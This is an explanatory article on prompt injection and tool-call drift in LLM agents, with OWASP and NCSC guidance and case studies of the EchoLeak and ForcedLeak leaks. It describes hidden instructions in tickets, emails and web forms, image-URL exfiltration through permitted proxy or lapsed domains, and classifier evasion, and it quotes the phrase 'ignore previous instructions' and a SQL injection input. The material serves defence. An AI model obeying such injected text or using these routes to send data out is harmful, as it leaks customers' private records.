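# Prompt injection and tool-call drift in enterprise systems built on language models, and how well the usual controls work

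## How language models come to read hostile text and call changing tools

A language model is a program that takes in text and produces a likely continuation. Companies now connect these models to email, documents, customer databases and other internal software so that the models can take actions as well as answer questions. They usually do this with an agent, which is a language model that runs in a loop, requests actions and receives the results as more text. The agent acts through tools, which are ordinary software functions that the company or an outside supplier provides.

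This arrangement has two security problems. In prompt injection, text makes the model do something its developer or user did not intend. In tool-call drift, tool use comes to differ from what someone reviewed. An attacker can cause either, but drift also occurs without an attack, for instance when a supplier ships an update. Companies mostly rely on four controls: input sanitisation, allow-lists, version pinning of tool definitions, and audit logging. Both problems follow from how a model receives its text and how a tool call reaches the software that carries it out.

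### One request through a support assistant

A support assistant might have three tools. `read_ticket` fetches the text of a customer's complaint, `lookup_customer` returns a record from the customer database, and `send_email` sends a message from the company's support address. A support employee types a request to answer ticket 4812.

The model never receives that sentence alone. The software around it first assembles a longer text, which opens with the system instructions, where the developer describes the job and its rules. Then come the tool definitions. Each has a name, a description in plain language, and a schema, meaning a list of the arguments the tool accepts and their types. The definition of `send_email` might look like this:

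```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "description": "Send a reply to the customer who opened the ticket.",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "to": { "type": "string" },
      "body": { "type": "string" }
    },
    "required": ["to", "body"]
  }
}
```

According to *Define tools*, part of Anthropic's documentation for its Claude models, the company's interface combines the tool definitions, tool settings and any developer instructions into a single system prompt. Whoever writes a tool's description is therefore writing part of the prompt.

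The support worker's message follows. Many assistants also add retrieved text here, such as help-centre articles from a search. The software converts all of it into tokens, the short numbered pieces of text on which a model operates. OpenAI (2025) published the complete layout that its gpt-oss models use, called Harmony. Special tokens mark where each message begins and ends, and a header gives the message a role: system, developer, user, assistant or tool. When instructions conflict, the model should prioritise them in that order, with tool results last. But the markers are tokens in the same sequence as everything else, and the priority order is a tendency the model learned in training, which no separate mechanism enforces.

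The model produces a call to `read_ticket` with the argument 4812 from this sequence. The surrounding software runs the function, appends the ticket's text as a new message, and sends the whole sequence back to the model. Anthropic's format instead puts the result in a labeled block inside a new user message. The model then calls `lookup_customer` to get the order history, calls `send_email` with a reply, and finishes with a short summary for the support worker.

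By this point the sequence contains text from the developer, the tools' suppliers, the support worker and the person who wrote the ticket, who could be anyone with an email address.

### Direct and indirect injection

Simon Willison named the attack in September 2022 in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (2022), which described an example Riley Goodside had posted the day before. Goodside had instructed OpenAI's GPT-3 to translate a text from English to French. The text was an instruction to ignore the directions above and output "Haha pwned!!", which GPT-3 did. It did the same when Goodside used a longer prompt warning that the text might contain directions designed to trick the model. Willison saw a security problem because developers were already building products by adding users' input to prompts written in advance.

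Goodside's example is direct injection, in which the attacker types into the system. Only staff can type into the support assistant, and a dishonest employee gains little by attacking it this way unless the assistant has wider access than the employee. Such wider access is common enough to be worth checking for.

Indirect injection lets an attacker influence a model without direct access to it, by planting instructions in material that the model is likely to retrieve. Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023) introduced the technique in *Not what you've signed up for*. They demonstrated attacks on Bing's GPT-4-based chat service, on code-completion engines, and on their own test applications. When Bing's chat was open in the browser's sidebar, instructions on the current web page could steer the model even if the user could not see them. They also listed emails, code repositories and images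 as possible routes, along with short injections that make the model fetch longer ones. One attack they anticipated is very close to the case of the support assistant. In it, a personal assistant reads mail containing instructions, opens private data, and sends mail accordingly.

Suppose ticket 4812 contains a plausible complaint about a late parcel, followed by a paragraph headed "Support policy" in white text on a white background. The paragraph tells the assistant to look up another customer and email the record to an outside address. `read_ticket` returns both parts as plain text, so the model cannot see that the paragraph was hidden. If the model follows it, it calls `lookup_customer` with a valid name and `send_email` with a valid address, and the attacker needs neither a software exploit nor a stolen password.

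Security engineers have long called this pattern a confused deputy, meaning a program with high privileges that someone with lower privileges tricks into acting for them. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies. David C writes that, in the worst case, an attacker could do anything that direct access to the same tools would allow. For the support assistant, that means sending any customer's record to any address.

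This particular theft requires all three tools. `read_ticket` brings in text from strangers, `lookup_customer` opens private data, and `send_email` can carry data out. The official Model Context Protocol blog (2026) noted more generally in March that users routinely mix tools from several suppliers in one session, so the risk depends on all the tools in the session. A review that approves each tool separately can miss this risk.

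### Why the fix for SQL injection does not carry over

Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, a nearly thirty-year-old attack on databases. Programs query most databases in SQL. If a website builds a query by pasting a visitor's name between two quotation marks, a visitor can enter `'; drop table users;` to close the quotation early. The database then treats the rest as a second command, which deletes the table.

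Parameterised queries prevent this. The program sends the database a query with a placeholder, `select * from users where username = ?`, and supplies the name separately. The database fixes the structure of the command before it inserts the name, so no name can become a command.

Willison hoped that language models could also take instructions through one input and data through another. One OpenAI model already did this, but injections in the data still worked on it. Goodside suggested putting the untrusted text inside a quoted string, but Brian Mastenbrook found a way around that. Four days after naming the attack, Willison admitted in *I don’t know how to solve prompt injection* (2022) that he knew how to beat SQL injection but had no reliable way to beat prompt injection. In April 2023 he added a note to the post that had named the attack, saying that the "parameterized prompts" he had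 wished for looked extremely difficult, if not impossible, on the current architecture of language models.

*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) compares prompt injection with three older attacks in which a system treats data as commands: buffer overflows, SQL injection, and cross-site scripting, where an attacker gets a website to run a script in other people's browsers. Structural changes dealt with all three, rather than better recognition of malicious input. With SQL, for example, a parser can separate code from data. Ordinary language has no such boundary, and training teaches models to follow instructions wherever they appear. David C makes the same argument from how models process text, where "there is only ever 'next token'", so a label reading "the following is data" is just more text the model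 uses to predict the next token.

This argument is about guarantees and does not show that any given injection will succeed. Narisetty and colleagues grant that filters and special training hold some attacks to low success rates and are useful as one layer among several. David C likewise says only that prompt injection may never be fully mitigated in the way SQL injection can be. Still, a company that has fixed SQL injection can stop worrying about odd usernames, while nobody can yet assure the owner of the support assistant that odd tickets are safe. This is a large part of why OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes security guidance, puts prompt injection first on its list of risks for applications built on language models.

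### How data leaves through a link or an image

Data could still leak if `send_email` were removed. Most chat windows display the model's output as formatted text, with working links and images. An image in this format is a web address that the browser fetches automatically. The hostile ticket can therefore include an instruction to end the summary with an image whose address points to the attacker's server and includes the customer's details. When the browser requests the image, it sends those details to the attacker. The image can be a single transparent pixel, and the support worker does not have to click anything.

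A link works the same way, except that the user has to click it. Greshake and colleagues noted that ChatGPT would build links from injected text, which lets an attacker hide the real address behind a trustworthy-looking label.

Browsers have a defence against this that is older than language models, called a Content Security Policy. It is a set of rules, sent by a website with its pages, that lists where the browser may load scripts, images and other content from. Web developers adopted it largely to defend against cross-site scripting. If the support tool's policy permits images only from the company's own domain, the browser will not fetch the attacker's picture. The browser makes this check outside the model, so neither the wording of a ticket nor the model's output can affect it.

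However, such a policy does not usually stop a person from following a link. It also checks a request's destination but not its contents, so a permitted domain that fetches other addresses or forwards requests to them on demand will pass the data along.

### Listing and calling tools

The company could write all three tools itself, but often some come from elsewhere, and the assistant then needs a common way to find and use them. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a widely used open standard for this. A supplier runs a server that offers tools, and the assistant's software connects to it as a client.

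Clients use tools mainly through two requests. With `tools/list`, the client requests the available tools, and the server returns their definitions. With `tools/call`, the client sends a tool's name and arguments, and the server returns a result. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the specification page for the revision of 28 July 2026, illustrates both with a weather service. The listing describes `get_weather` and its one required argument, a location. The call supplies "New York", and the server returns a line of text with the temperature. The specification also recommends that a person be able to refuse any call, but a client without this option still conforms.

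On drift, Kim and Kang (2026) point out in *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning* that an ordinary tool call doesn't identify the definition the model was given or the code that should run. The client and server agree on a protocol version, but the standard fields of a tool definition don't include a version for the tool itself.

The specification also allows a server to change its list of tools over time and recommends that it send a notice when it does, but under the July revision only clients that have subscribed to these notices receive them. A client may also keep a copy of the list to avoid repeated requests, for five minutes in the Model Context Protocol (2026) documentation's example. An agent can therefore work for some minutes from a definition that the server has already replaced. This is usually harmless, but the protocol links the tool that the company approved to the tool that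 runs only by name, so a server can keep the name and change everything else.

### Three kinds of tool-call drift

"Tool-call drift" has no settled definition, and researchers writing in 2026 have used similar terms for different things. In *Robust Function Calling for LLM Agents Under Interface Drift*, Chattopadhyay, Halder and Roy (2026) study harmless changes to descriptions, schemas and tool lists that leave the tools' function the same. Kim and Kang use "schema-epoch drift" for cases where the model forms a call under one version of a tool but the call runs under another, with a different effect. In *Memory-Induced Tool-Drift in LLM Agents* (2026), Dabas, Jeong and colleagues use "tool-drift" for changes in the arguments a model picks. *Authorization Drift in LLM Agents* (2026) is about whether an agent stays within its authority over a task of many steps.

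The broad definition, a gap between reviewed and actual tool use, covers all of these. It helps to group them by where the change happens, because a check in one place will not detect a change in another.

First, the tool definition can change. For example, the supplier of `send_email` might rename the argument `to` as `recipient`, add an optional field for blind copies, or rewrite the description. Chattopadhyay and colleagues also include cases where the definition stays the same but new tools with overlapping descriptions are added, which gives the model more chances to pick the wrong one. Most such changes are routine maintenance, but a hostile supplier can wait until the tool is approved and then add an instruction to the description, which goes straight into the prompt. This attack, which security writers call a "rug pull", is both drift and prompt injection.

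Second, the tool's behavior can change while its definition stays the same. `lookup_customer` might begin to return payment details along with the order history. Kim and Kang found that version 0.22.2 of DBHub, a server that connects agents to databases, changed a database's contents in what was supposed to be read-only mode, while version 0.22.6 rejected the same call. The relevant definition was the same in both versions. (They also traced a GitHub tool whose default setting changed between versions.) Comparing definitions cannot reveal this kind of drift.

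Third, the model's choice of tools or arguments can change while the tools stay the same. The cause may be a new model version, an edit to the system instructions, or the notes that some agents keep about their users. In an example from Dabas and colleagues, an agent remembers that its user likes to skim novels, and so sets a validation check to "quick" when a large merge of product data calls for "comprehensive". Similarly, the support assistant might stop calling `lookup_customer` for a worker whose stored profile mentions impatience, and answer from the ticket alone. An injected ticket also changes what the model chooses, though usually for only one session. Inspecting the tools would not reveal a problem in either case.

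### The four controls and the build phase

Input sanitisation usually means putting a filter between `read_ticket` and the model. The filter looks for text that resembles an instruction and either removes it or rejects the ticket. This control acts earliest of the four, but a hostile instruction can be worded in any way, and experiments are needed to show how well filters work against attackers who keep rewording.

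An allow-list specifies which tools, arguments or destinations are permitted. A policy layer, which is code outside the model, checks each call before it runs and blocks anything not on the list. The support assistant could then email only the address on the open ticket, even if the ticket's text led the model to try another address.

Version pinning records the exact release or definition of each tool that the company approved, often as a hash (a short fingerprint of the text or file), and stops the assistant when the current version differs. If the server returned a definition of `send_email` with an extra sentence, the assistant would wait until someone had reviewed the sentence.

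Audit logging keeps a protected record of what the assistant read, which calls it made, under whose authority and with what result. It doesn't block anything by itself, but it lets the company trace a leaked customer record back to ticket 4812.

All four depend on choices made in the build phase, before the assistant goes into daily use. During this phase, the company picks the tools, sets their permissions, decides which versions count as approved, and designs the log. It can revise any of this later, but doing so takes extra work.

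Combining tools can improve a model's accuracy, but it makes permissions harder to control. Anthropic advises developers to offer fewer, more capable tools, for example one tool with an `action` argument in place of separate tools to create, review and merge a code change, because fewer choices are less likely to confuse the model. A rule that permits the combined tool by name then permits merging as well as reviewing, so the policy layer must also inspect arguments. Names are easier to check because, as the Agentic AI Foundation explains, the protocol now requires clients that connect over the web to put the tool's name in a header, where a gateway can read it without opening the request. Arguments stay in the body unless the tool's author has marked them for copying. A company that decides after launch to split the tool up again must rewrite its instructions, repeat its tests, and find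 every rule and program that mentions the old name.

Tool permissions tend to stay broad because colleagues soon come to depend on them. If `lookup_customer` starts out with access to the whole database because that was quickest to build, narrowing that access later will break something of theirs. Changes to tool definitions are hard to detect when a company has kept no copy of the versions it approved. It cannot tell whether today's definitions are different and has to review them all again.

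Gaps in logs are the hardest to fix, because nobody can go back and record what the assistant read last month. Even a carefully designed log format can depend on a protocol feature that later changes. The July revision removed the protocol's session identifier, according to the Model Context Protocol (2026) changelog, so any log that used it to link the calls in one conversation needs a substitute. The same revision documents a way to attach tracing identifiers to requests, which would work as a substitute, but only for calls made after the company adopts it.

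## What OWASP and the UK's cyber agency recommend

Two published sources advise developers to expect that attackers will sometimes fool the model, and to limit the damage when they do. One is the OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications, a ranked list of security risks in software built on large language models (LLMs), which OWASP revised in August 2026. The other is David C's post for the National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), the UK government's cyber security agency.

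### Who writes the OWASP list

OWASP is best known for its older list of the top ten risks to ordinary web applications. Its publications are free and have no legal force, but according to Respan (2026), which sells security testing for agents, auditors and corporate buyers treat them as a baseline.

OWASP's GenAI Security Project writes the list for language models. OWASP (2026) credits the current edition to hundreds of AI security experts. The project takes sponsorship from security companies. Steve Wilson, who founded the list and led the new edition with Rock Lambros, is an executive at one such company, Exabeam. *The hardest AI security problems now live in what an agent is...* (Constantin, 2026) advises readers to keep both roles in mind when Wilson recommends controls.

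### The 2023, 2025 and 2026 editions

The table, based on Respan's mapping, shows where each 2026 entry appeared in earlier editions, sometimes under another name. A dash means the edition had no such entry.

| 2026 entry | What it covers | 2026 | 2025 | 2023 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt Injection | Input that changes the model's behavior in ways the developer did not intend | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Sensitive Information Disclosure | Confidential data reaching an unauthorised channel | 2 | 2 | 6 |
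| Excessive Agency | More tools, permissions or independence than the job needs | 3 | 6 | 8 |
| Supply Chain | Untrustworthy models, data and add-ons from outside | 4 | 3 | 5 |
| Data and Model Poisoning | Tampering with data that a model learns from or retrieves | 5 | 4 | 3 |
| Unbounded Consumption | Uncontrolled use that runs up costs or blocks the service | 6 | 10 | 4 |
| Misinformation | Wrong output that people or software rely on | 7 | 9 | 9 |
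| Hidden Context Exposure | Leaks of system instructions, tool schemas and similar text | 8 | 7 | – |
| Vector and Embedding Weaknesses | Flaws in the search systems that choose text for the model | 9 | 8 | – |
| Improper Output Handling | Passing model output to other software without checking it | 10 | 5 | 2 |

The 2023 edition also had an entry called Insecure Plugin Design, plugins being an earlier form of tool. OWASP dropped the entry in 2025 and split its content between Excessive Agency, which covers what a tool is allowed to do, and Supply Chain, which covers where the tool came from. A tool that changes after approval can fall under both.

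Improper Output Handling has fallen furthest since 2023, although OWASP widened it in 2026 to include chat windows that automatically fetch outside resources named in the model's output. The one-pixel image could leak a customer's details this way. Advait Patel, an engineer who created another OWASP tool, told ReversingLabs that the entry dropped because the risks above it had become more urgent, and that output handling had not become safe.

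The reordering also creates some work for companies that refer to entries by number. LLM06 was Excessive Agency in the 2025 edition and is now Unbounded Consumption, so a reviewer reading an old security questionnaire that cites LLM06 without a year could look up the wrong risk.

### How votes and incidents produce the ranking

Practitioners' votes alone decided the earlier rankings. For 2026, the project also collected 7,714 incident records from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms involving AI. Software classifiers found that 6,639 of the records had enough detail to sort into categories. The vote counted for three quarters of the ranking and the incidents for one quarter.

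The project leaders kept the vote dominant because they see the list as a consensus product and did not want one noisy year of data to overturn it. As a hypothetical example, suppose OWASP scored each risk from 0 to 100 on both measures and took a weighted average. A risk with 100 from the voters and 10 from the incidents would get 0.75 × 100 + 0.25 × 10 = 77.5, while a risk with 60 from the voters and 100 from the incidents would get 70. A clear favourite among voters can therefore stay first with few recorded incidents.

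Misinformation had the widest gap in the other direction. It ranked near the bottom in the vote but near the top in the incident record, and it finished seventh. Excessive Agency rose to third because votes and incidents both supported the move. A commentary from the Japanese IT company NTTデータ先端技術, *なぜ今、OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 2026を読むべきか 第2回* (2026), notes that OWASP added little to the text of that entry and concludes that dangers already foreseen are now appearing in practice.

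### Why injection ranks first with so few recorded incidents

If OWASP had ranked by incident count alone, prompt injection would have fallen outside the top ten. OWASP, quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*, explains that security teams fight injection hard, so fewer clean exploits reach public databases and the count understates the risk. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a blog post from a company that sells security testing, goes further and takes the low count as evidence that the defences work.

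The count alone cannot show this, because it would look the same if practitioners simply overrated injection. They might overrate it because it is the best-known attack on language models and is easy to demonstrate, and some of the voters presumably sell products against it. Patel told ReversingLabs that the vote reflects what practitioners worry about, while the incidents reflect what has caused harm. OWASP's explanation is also hard to reconcile with Wilson's view, in the same article, that attackers improve their injections faster than models learn to detect them. If Wilson is right, then either controls outside the models keep the count low or the databases miss many attacks.

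OWASP's count may also miss many injections if the classifiers gave each incident only one label. If an attacker used ticket 4812 to steal a customer's record, for example, the incident would involve injection, excessive agency and disclosure of sensitive information, but it might be counted under only one of the last two. And a plain count gives a trivial incident the same weight as a serious one.

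Better data could show which of these explanations is right. If defence explains the low count, companies with weak defences should suffer more injection incidents per system than similar companies with strong ones, and logs should show frequent attempts even where few succeed. If practitioners overrate the risk, successful attacks should be rare in both groups. Relabelling the 6,639 incidents with every contributing cause would show how many injections are counted under other causes. A company could also switch off a defence in a test copy of its own system and measure how much the attack success rate rises, though this wouldn't show how often anyone attempts an attack.

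Public databases are a poor source for most of this because companies can often keep incidents private. Mandatory reporting would help, but existing rules may miss many relevant cases. Since 11 September 2026, the EU's Cyber Resilience Act has required manufacturers to warn their national response team within 24 hours when attackers are actively exploiting a vulnerability. Constantin notes that the act governs products, not how a company deploys an agent. An injection that succeeds because a company gave its assistant too much access may therefore never appear in those reports.

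A company can narrow an agent's permissions without settling this dispute. Votes and incidents are consistent on Excessive Agency, and narrower permissions limit the damage from both attacks and the model's own mistakes. The dispute matters more when a company decides how much to spend on input filters.

### Designing for a model that attackers will fool

OWASP's central advice to developers in the 2026 edition is to "stop trying to build a model that cannot be fooled" and instead build the surrounding system so that nothing important breaks when the model is fooled. For prompt injection, this means assuming that attackers will eventually get past the model's instructions, and restricting both what the model may do and where its output may go.

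The new edition differs from the previous one mostly in emphasis. In *LLM01:2025 Prompt Injection*, OWASP already doubted that any prevention method was fool-proof, and it recommended minimal access and human approval for high-risk actions. But the first of the seven measures it listed was to write better system instructions, including an instruction to ignore attempts to change them. In June 2026, two months before the new edition, the OWASP researcher Ariel Fogel still called injection an "unresolved problem" (Poireault, 2026, *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*).

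The support assistant matches an example in OWASP's 2026 entry on injection. In that example, an attacker plants text in a trusted channel that people with few privileges can write to, such as a support ticket or feedback form, and turns the user's model into a confused deputy.

OWASP traces Excessive Agency to three causes, and the support assistant could easily have all of them. It has excessive functionality if `send_email` can write to any address when the assistant only needs to reply to customers. It has excessive permissions if `lookup_customer` only needs to read records but connects through a database account that can also change and delete them. It has excessive autonomy if it sends a customer's record outside the company without anyone confirming the message.

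OWASP recommends addressing the problem in ordinary code instead of in the prompt. According to Respan, trusted code should hold the credentials and give each operation only the access it needs. A policy layer should then recheck privileged calls, including their arguments, when they run. Wilson's own list is similar: read-only tools instead of general connectors, requests made under the user's limited identity, a policy check between the model and other systems, and human approval for anything hard to reverse.

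A policy layer that restricts `send_email` to the ticket's author would stop the theft by email, but not a false or rude reply to that author. Dave Hayes of FusionAuth, a company that sells login software, told ReversingLabs that nobody can guarantee a model will resist manipulation, but developers can write fixed rules for what it may do afterwards.

Larry Maccherone, founder of the software company Lumenize, told ReversingLabs that the advice could lead companies to accumulate approval steps and policy engines. An agent produces new behavior each time it runs, so nobody can approve it in advance the way a reviewer approves a fixed program. Maccherone would focus on detecting failures quickly and letting the system adapt, and argues that an agent needs considerable freedom to find and repair its own security gaps.

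This is a fair objection to any plan that depends on predicting what an agent will do. It is weaker against a limit on recipients, because the policy layer can refuse an outside address even if nobody predicted why the model would choose it. Detection also comes too late for some harms, since a company cannot take back a customer's record once an attacker has it. Maccherone's point about the downside of restrictions still stands, because each one can also block something the assistant legitimately needs to do.

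### Which entries support each control

The next table matches the four controls to five OWASP entries: Prompt Injection, Excessive Agency, Supply Chain, Hidden Context Exposure and Improper Output Handling. Most of the table is based on Respan's account of the 2026 edition, but the advice on filtering comes from OWASP's 2025 page.

| Control | Relevant entries | Advice | Gap |
|---|---|---|---|
| Input sanitisation | Prompt Injection | Filter input and output, and mark outside text as untrusted | No filter is known to be fool-proof |
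| Allow-lists | Excessive Agency, Prompt Injection, Hidden Context Exposure, Improper Output Handling | Offer fewer and narrower tools, and check calls and output outside the model | Each company must write its own rules |
| Version pinning | Supply Chain | Verify model files with hashes and signatures | No mention of pinning tool definitions |
| Audit logging | None of the five | None beyond protecting logs, under Sensitive Information Disclosure | No guidance on what to record |

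Allow-lists have the broadest support. Hidden Context Exposure belongs in that row because developers sometimes write their access rules into the system instructions. OWASP advises them to assume outsiders can discover this text and to keep passwords and other secrets out of it. The text should also never be the only control on who may do what, according to an SC Media article produced with OWASP. An instruction such as "only email the customer who opened the ticket" goes against this advice if nothing else enforces it. An attacker who extracts the instruction also learns which rule to get around.

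In its advice on Unbounded Consumption, OWASP recommends isolating the model from networks and internal services it does not need, which also makes it harder for an attacker to send data out. A company that reads only the entry on prompt injection could miss this recommendation.

For input sanitisation, the 2025 page recommends both simple checks for forbidden strings and filters that judge meaning. It also recommends using ordinary code to check the format of the model's output. A format check can catch a reply with a missing field, but it would miss the theft through ticket 4812, because the stolen record would travel in a correctly formed email.

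The gap on pinning is important for tool-call drift. The Supply Chain category, as Respan describes it, includes model files that differ from their documentation, and hashes and signatures are sensible protection against that. But a company could verify every model file and still accept a rewritten description of `send_email`. Hashes work for tool definitions too, but readers would have to make that connection themselves.

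### The separate list for agents

OWASP now divides its advice between two lists. The list for LLM applications covers risks that arise when the model is part of an application. The OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications covers models that can call tools, keep memory between sessions, and affect other systems. The risks on this list include attackers redirecting an agent's goals, misuse of tools, abuse of privileges, and poisoned memory. OWASP published the first edition of the agentic list on 9 December 2025, according to CyberSaint's *What is the OWASP Top 10 for LLM and Agentic AI*.

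Many systems fall under both lists, and OWASP advises companies to read them together. The support assistant is a component when it summarises a ticket and an actor when it sends an email, and one hostile ticket can affect it in both roles. Excessive Agency is largely about tools, but it stays on the list for LLM applications, with a cross-reference to the agentic list. A company that wants OWASP's advice on tools that change should therefore read the agentic list too, along with the Agent Control Standard, a specification for controlling agents while they run that OWASP recently took over.

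### What the NCSC adds

David C's argument that prompt injection has no equivalent of the parameterised query leads to much the same advice. OWASP makes the same comparison in its 2026 entry on injection. Wilson told ReversingLabs that when the list began, prompt injection had seemed comparable to SQL injection, which developers could largely avoid with enough care, but that the comparison had proved false. The two sources are not wholly independent, since David C cites OWASP's ranking. But the NCSC argument is based on how models process text, so doubts about OWASP's incident data do not weaken it.

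David C also uses the history of SQL injection as a warning. Attacks peaked around 2010, by which time many websites depended on SQL and few had protected themselves. Better defaults came only after a decade of breaches. Companies are now building language models into most kinds of software, and David C fears a similar wave of breaches if they don't plan for prompt injection.

Because no product can remove the risk, David C recommends that the people responsible for a system decide whether they can accept the risk that remains after the controls are in place. If they cannot, the task may be a poor use for a language model. He also warns buyers against any product said to "stop" prompt injection, and prefers suppliers who can explain how their product reduces the risk.

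The NCSC advice is more sceptical of filters than OWASP's 2025 page. David C is wary of blocking known bad phrases such as "ignore previous instructions", because an attacker can reword an attack in endless ways. Marking outside text, for example with labelled tags, can make attacks harder, but designers should put most of their effort into fixed safeguards that limit the system's actions.

For those limits, David C recommends a rule that came out of an online discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista. When a model processes text from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's level. This is stricter than Wilson's advice to run requests under the user's own identity. The support assistant's user is a support worker, who may well have permission to open every customer's record, so under Wilson's rule the hidden paragraph in ticket 4812 could still make the assistant open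 another customer's file. The NCSC rule would prevent this by giving the assistant only the ticket author's privileges while it handles the ticket.

The stricter rule is less practical. The software has to track who wrote each piece of text the model has read, and the assistant may lose access to internal notes that would help it answer an honest complaint. A company could have a model with no tools read the ticket and a separate program fetch the ticket author's own record. But the first model's output would still derive from the ticket, so passing it to a more privileged model would bring the problem back.

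The post gives the advice on logging that is missing from the table, though it does not cover version pinning. It says developers should first work out how an attacker might corrupt the system and what normal use looks like, then record enough to tell the two apart. That may include the model's full input and output, its tool use and its calls to other software. Failed calls deserve particular attention because an attacker will probably need several tries to refine an attack. If the support assistant tries to email three outside addresses and the policy layer blocks each attempt, the company has a chance to find the hostile ticket before the attacker sends a better one.

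Such a log would also hold every complaint and customer record the assistant had read. OWASP says confidential data can leak through logs, and it applies the same rules for classifying and removing sensitive data to logs and to the model's answers. The company therefore has to decide what to remove from its logs without deleting the text that would explain an attack.

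## Data leaks in Microsoft 365 Copilot and Salesforce Agentforce

In 2025, researchers stole data from two widely sold products, much as the attacker did through ticket 4812. Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions from their company's email, files and chats. Salesforce Agentforce lets companies build agents that work with their customer records. In both cases, an outsider sent in text through an ordinary channel, and an employee later asked the assistant for something routine. The answer included an image whose web address carried company data to a server the researchers controlled. Both vendors restricted the domains from which a browser could load images, but the researchers found a permitted domain that would pass the data on each time.

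### EchoLeak: from an email to an outside server

Aim Labs, the research arm of the security company Aim Security, found the Copilot flaw and named it EchoLeak. Its head, Itay Ravia, describes how it worked in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (2025). Only employees can use Copilot, but it searches their mailboxes along with the company's files and chats, and anyone can put text into a mailbox by sending an email. To get the attacker's email to come up in a search, Aim Labs wrote one long message covering many workplace topics, so that some part of it would match whatever an employee asked about. The employee never had to open the email or click on anything, which is why Aim Labs calls the attack "zero-click".

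Microsoft's first control was a classifier, a program trained to recognise injected instructions and keep them from reaching the model. Aim Labs got past it by wording the instructions as if they were meant for the email's recipient, without mentioning an AI assistant. Emails often ask people to gather information, so the text gave the classifier little to detect. Ravia adds that good collections of real injections are scarce, which makes such classifiers hard to train. Only tests with many attacks, not a single bypass, can measure how often a classifier fails.

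The second control removed links to outside websites from Copilot's answers. Copilot writes its answers in Markdown, a simple formatting language with several ways to write a link, and Microsoft's filter recognised the most common one but missed others. The filter had the same gap for images, which suited the attack better because they need no click. This was an ordinary programming mistake, and it can be fixed more completely than the classifier's failure. If the filter checked addresses after the software had converted the answer into a web page, it would no longer matter how the model wrote the link.

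The third control was the page's Content Security Policy. The attacker's domain was not on its list of permitted image sources, so the browser would not load images from it. Aim Labs then searched the permitted domains for one that would forward a request. A SharePoint service did this, but only if the employee had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A Microsoft Teams service that fetches web content on request did it without an invitation. The browser requested the image from Teams, and Teams requested it from the attacker's server, with the stolen data in the address. The policy allowed this, as designed, because the browser contacted only a permitted Microsoft domain.

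Copilot also normally names the documents behind an answer, which might have alerted the employee to a strange email. The attacker's email included an instruction not to mention the email, and Copilot complied. According to the academic case study *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), the victim would have seen at most a broken link or image.

As far as Aim Labs knew, customers' administrators had no setting that would have prevented the attack.

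### Outside text and inside data

Ravia argues that the deeper fault was that an email from outside the company could direct the model to data inside it. He calls this an "LLM scope violation", and Aim Labs sells a product meant to detect it. The NCSC's rule addresses the same fault: a model's privileges should drop to those of whoever wrote the text it is processing. Under that rule, Copilot could not have opened internal files while processing a stranger's email.

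The rule would make Copilot less useful, because employees use it to combine material from inside and outside the company. Someone preparing for a meeting with a supplier, for example, wants the supplier's emails and the company's own notes in one answer. Reddy and Gujral recommend separating the two kinds of text and controlling access according to where each piece came from. They write that Microsoft's patches reportedly added options to keep outside messages out of some Copilot answers, and they acknowledge that Copilot may then miss relevant information.

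They also suggest tagging outside text, which David C ranks well below fixed safeguards.

### Severity and exploitation of EchoLeak

Aim Labs reported the flaw to Microsoft in January 2025. Microsoft finished the repair on its own servers in May and published an advisory on 11 June, the day Aim Labs made its research public. Customers did not have to install anything.

The public vulnerability record, as reproduced by GCVE (2025), gives two severity scores on a ten-point scale: 9.3 from Microsoft and 7.5 from the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD). Both assessors gave the attack 3.9 for ease. The NVD added 3.6 for impact, counting only the loss of confidential data, for a total of 7.5. Microsoft gave 4.7 for impact because it also counted a small loss of data integrity and judged that the attack crossed a boundary between security domains. The scoring formula multiplies the sum by 1.08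 when an attack crosses such a boundary, so Microsoft's score is 1.08 × (4.7 + 3.9), or about 9.3. The assessors therefore disagree largely about whether a model that reads an outsider's email and then opens internal files has crossed a boundary, which on Ravia's account it clearly has.

No attacker is known to have used EchoLeak against a customer. Ravia reports that Microsoft confirmed this, and *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) repeats it. The US cyber agency CISA entered "none" under exploitation three days after the disclosure, and the entry was unchanged in November 2026. Because Microsoft runs the service, it can look for signs of an attack better than any customer can, but outsiders cannot easily check its statement.

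Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known case of someone weaponising an injection to steal data from a production system. That is somewhat overstated, because only the researchers are known to have run the attack. Ravia claims more narrowly that it was the first zero-click attack on a major AI application to cause concrete damage without depending on specific user behavior. Willison (2025) saw it as an extended version of attacks already found in a dozen products.

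### ForcedLeak: from a web form to customer records

Noma Security reported a similar flaw in Agentforce to Salesforce on 28 July 2025 and called it ForcedLeak. It affected companies that used Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature, which puts a form on a public website and saves each submission as a sales lead in the customer database. Noma rated the flaw 9.4 out of ten in its report, which the forum user Nytro (2025) reposted as *ForcedLeak*.

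Noma chose the form's description field because it accepted up to 42,000 characters, while the fields for names, company and email address had limits of between 40 and 80. The hidden instructions stayed in the database until an employee asked Agentforce to deal with the lead. Agentforce then followed both the employee's instructions and the hidden ones. It collected the email addresses of other leads and added an image to its answer whose URL contained those addresses.

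Salesforce also had a Content Security Policy. One of its 22 entries for image domains was `my-salesforce-cms.com`. The domain's registration had lapsed and the name was back on sale, so Noma bought it for $5. Browsers showing Agentforce's answers then sent the data to Noma's server, because the policy allowed the domain by name, regardless of who owned it.

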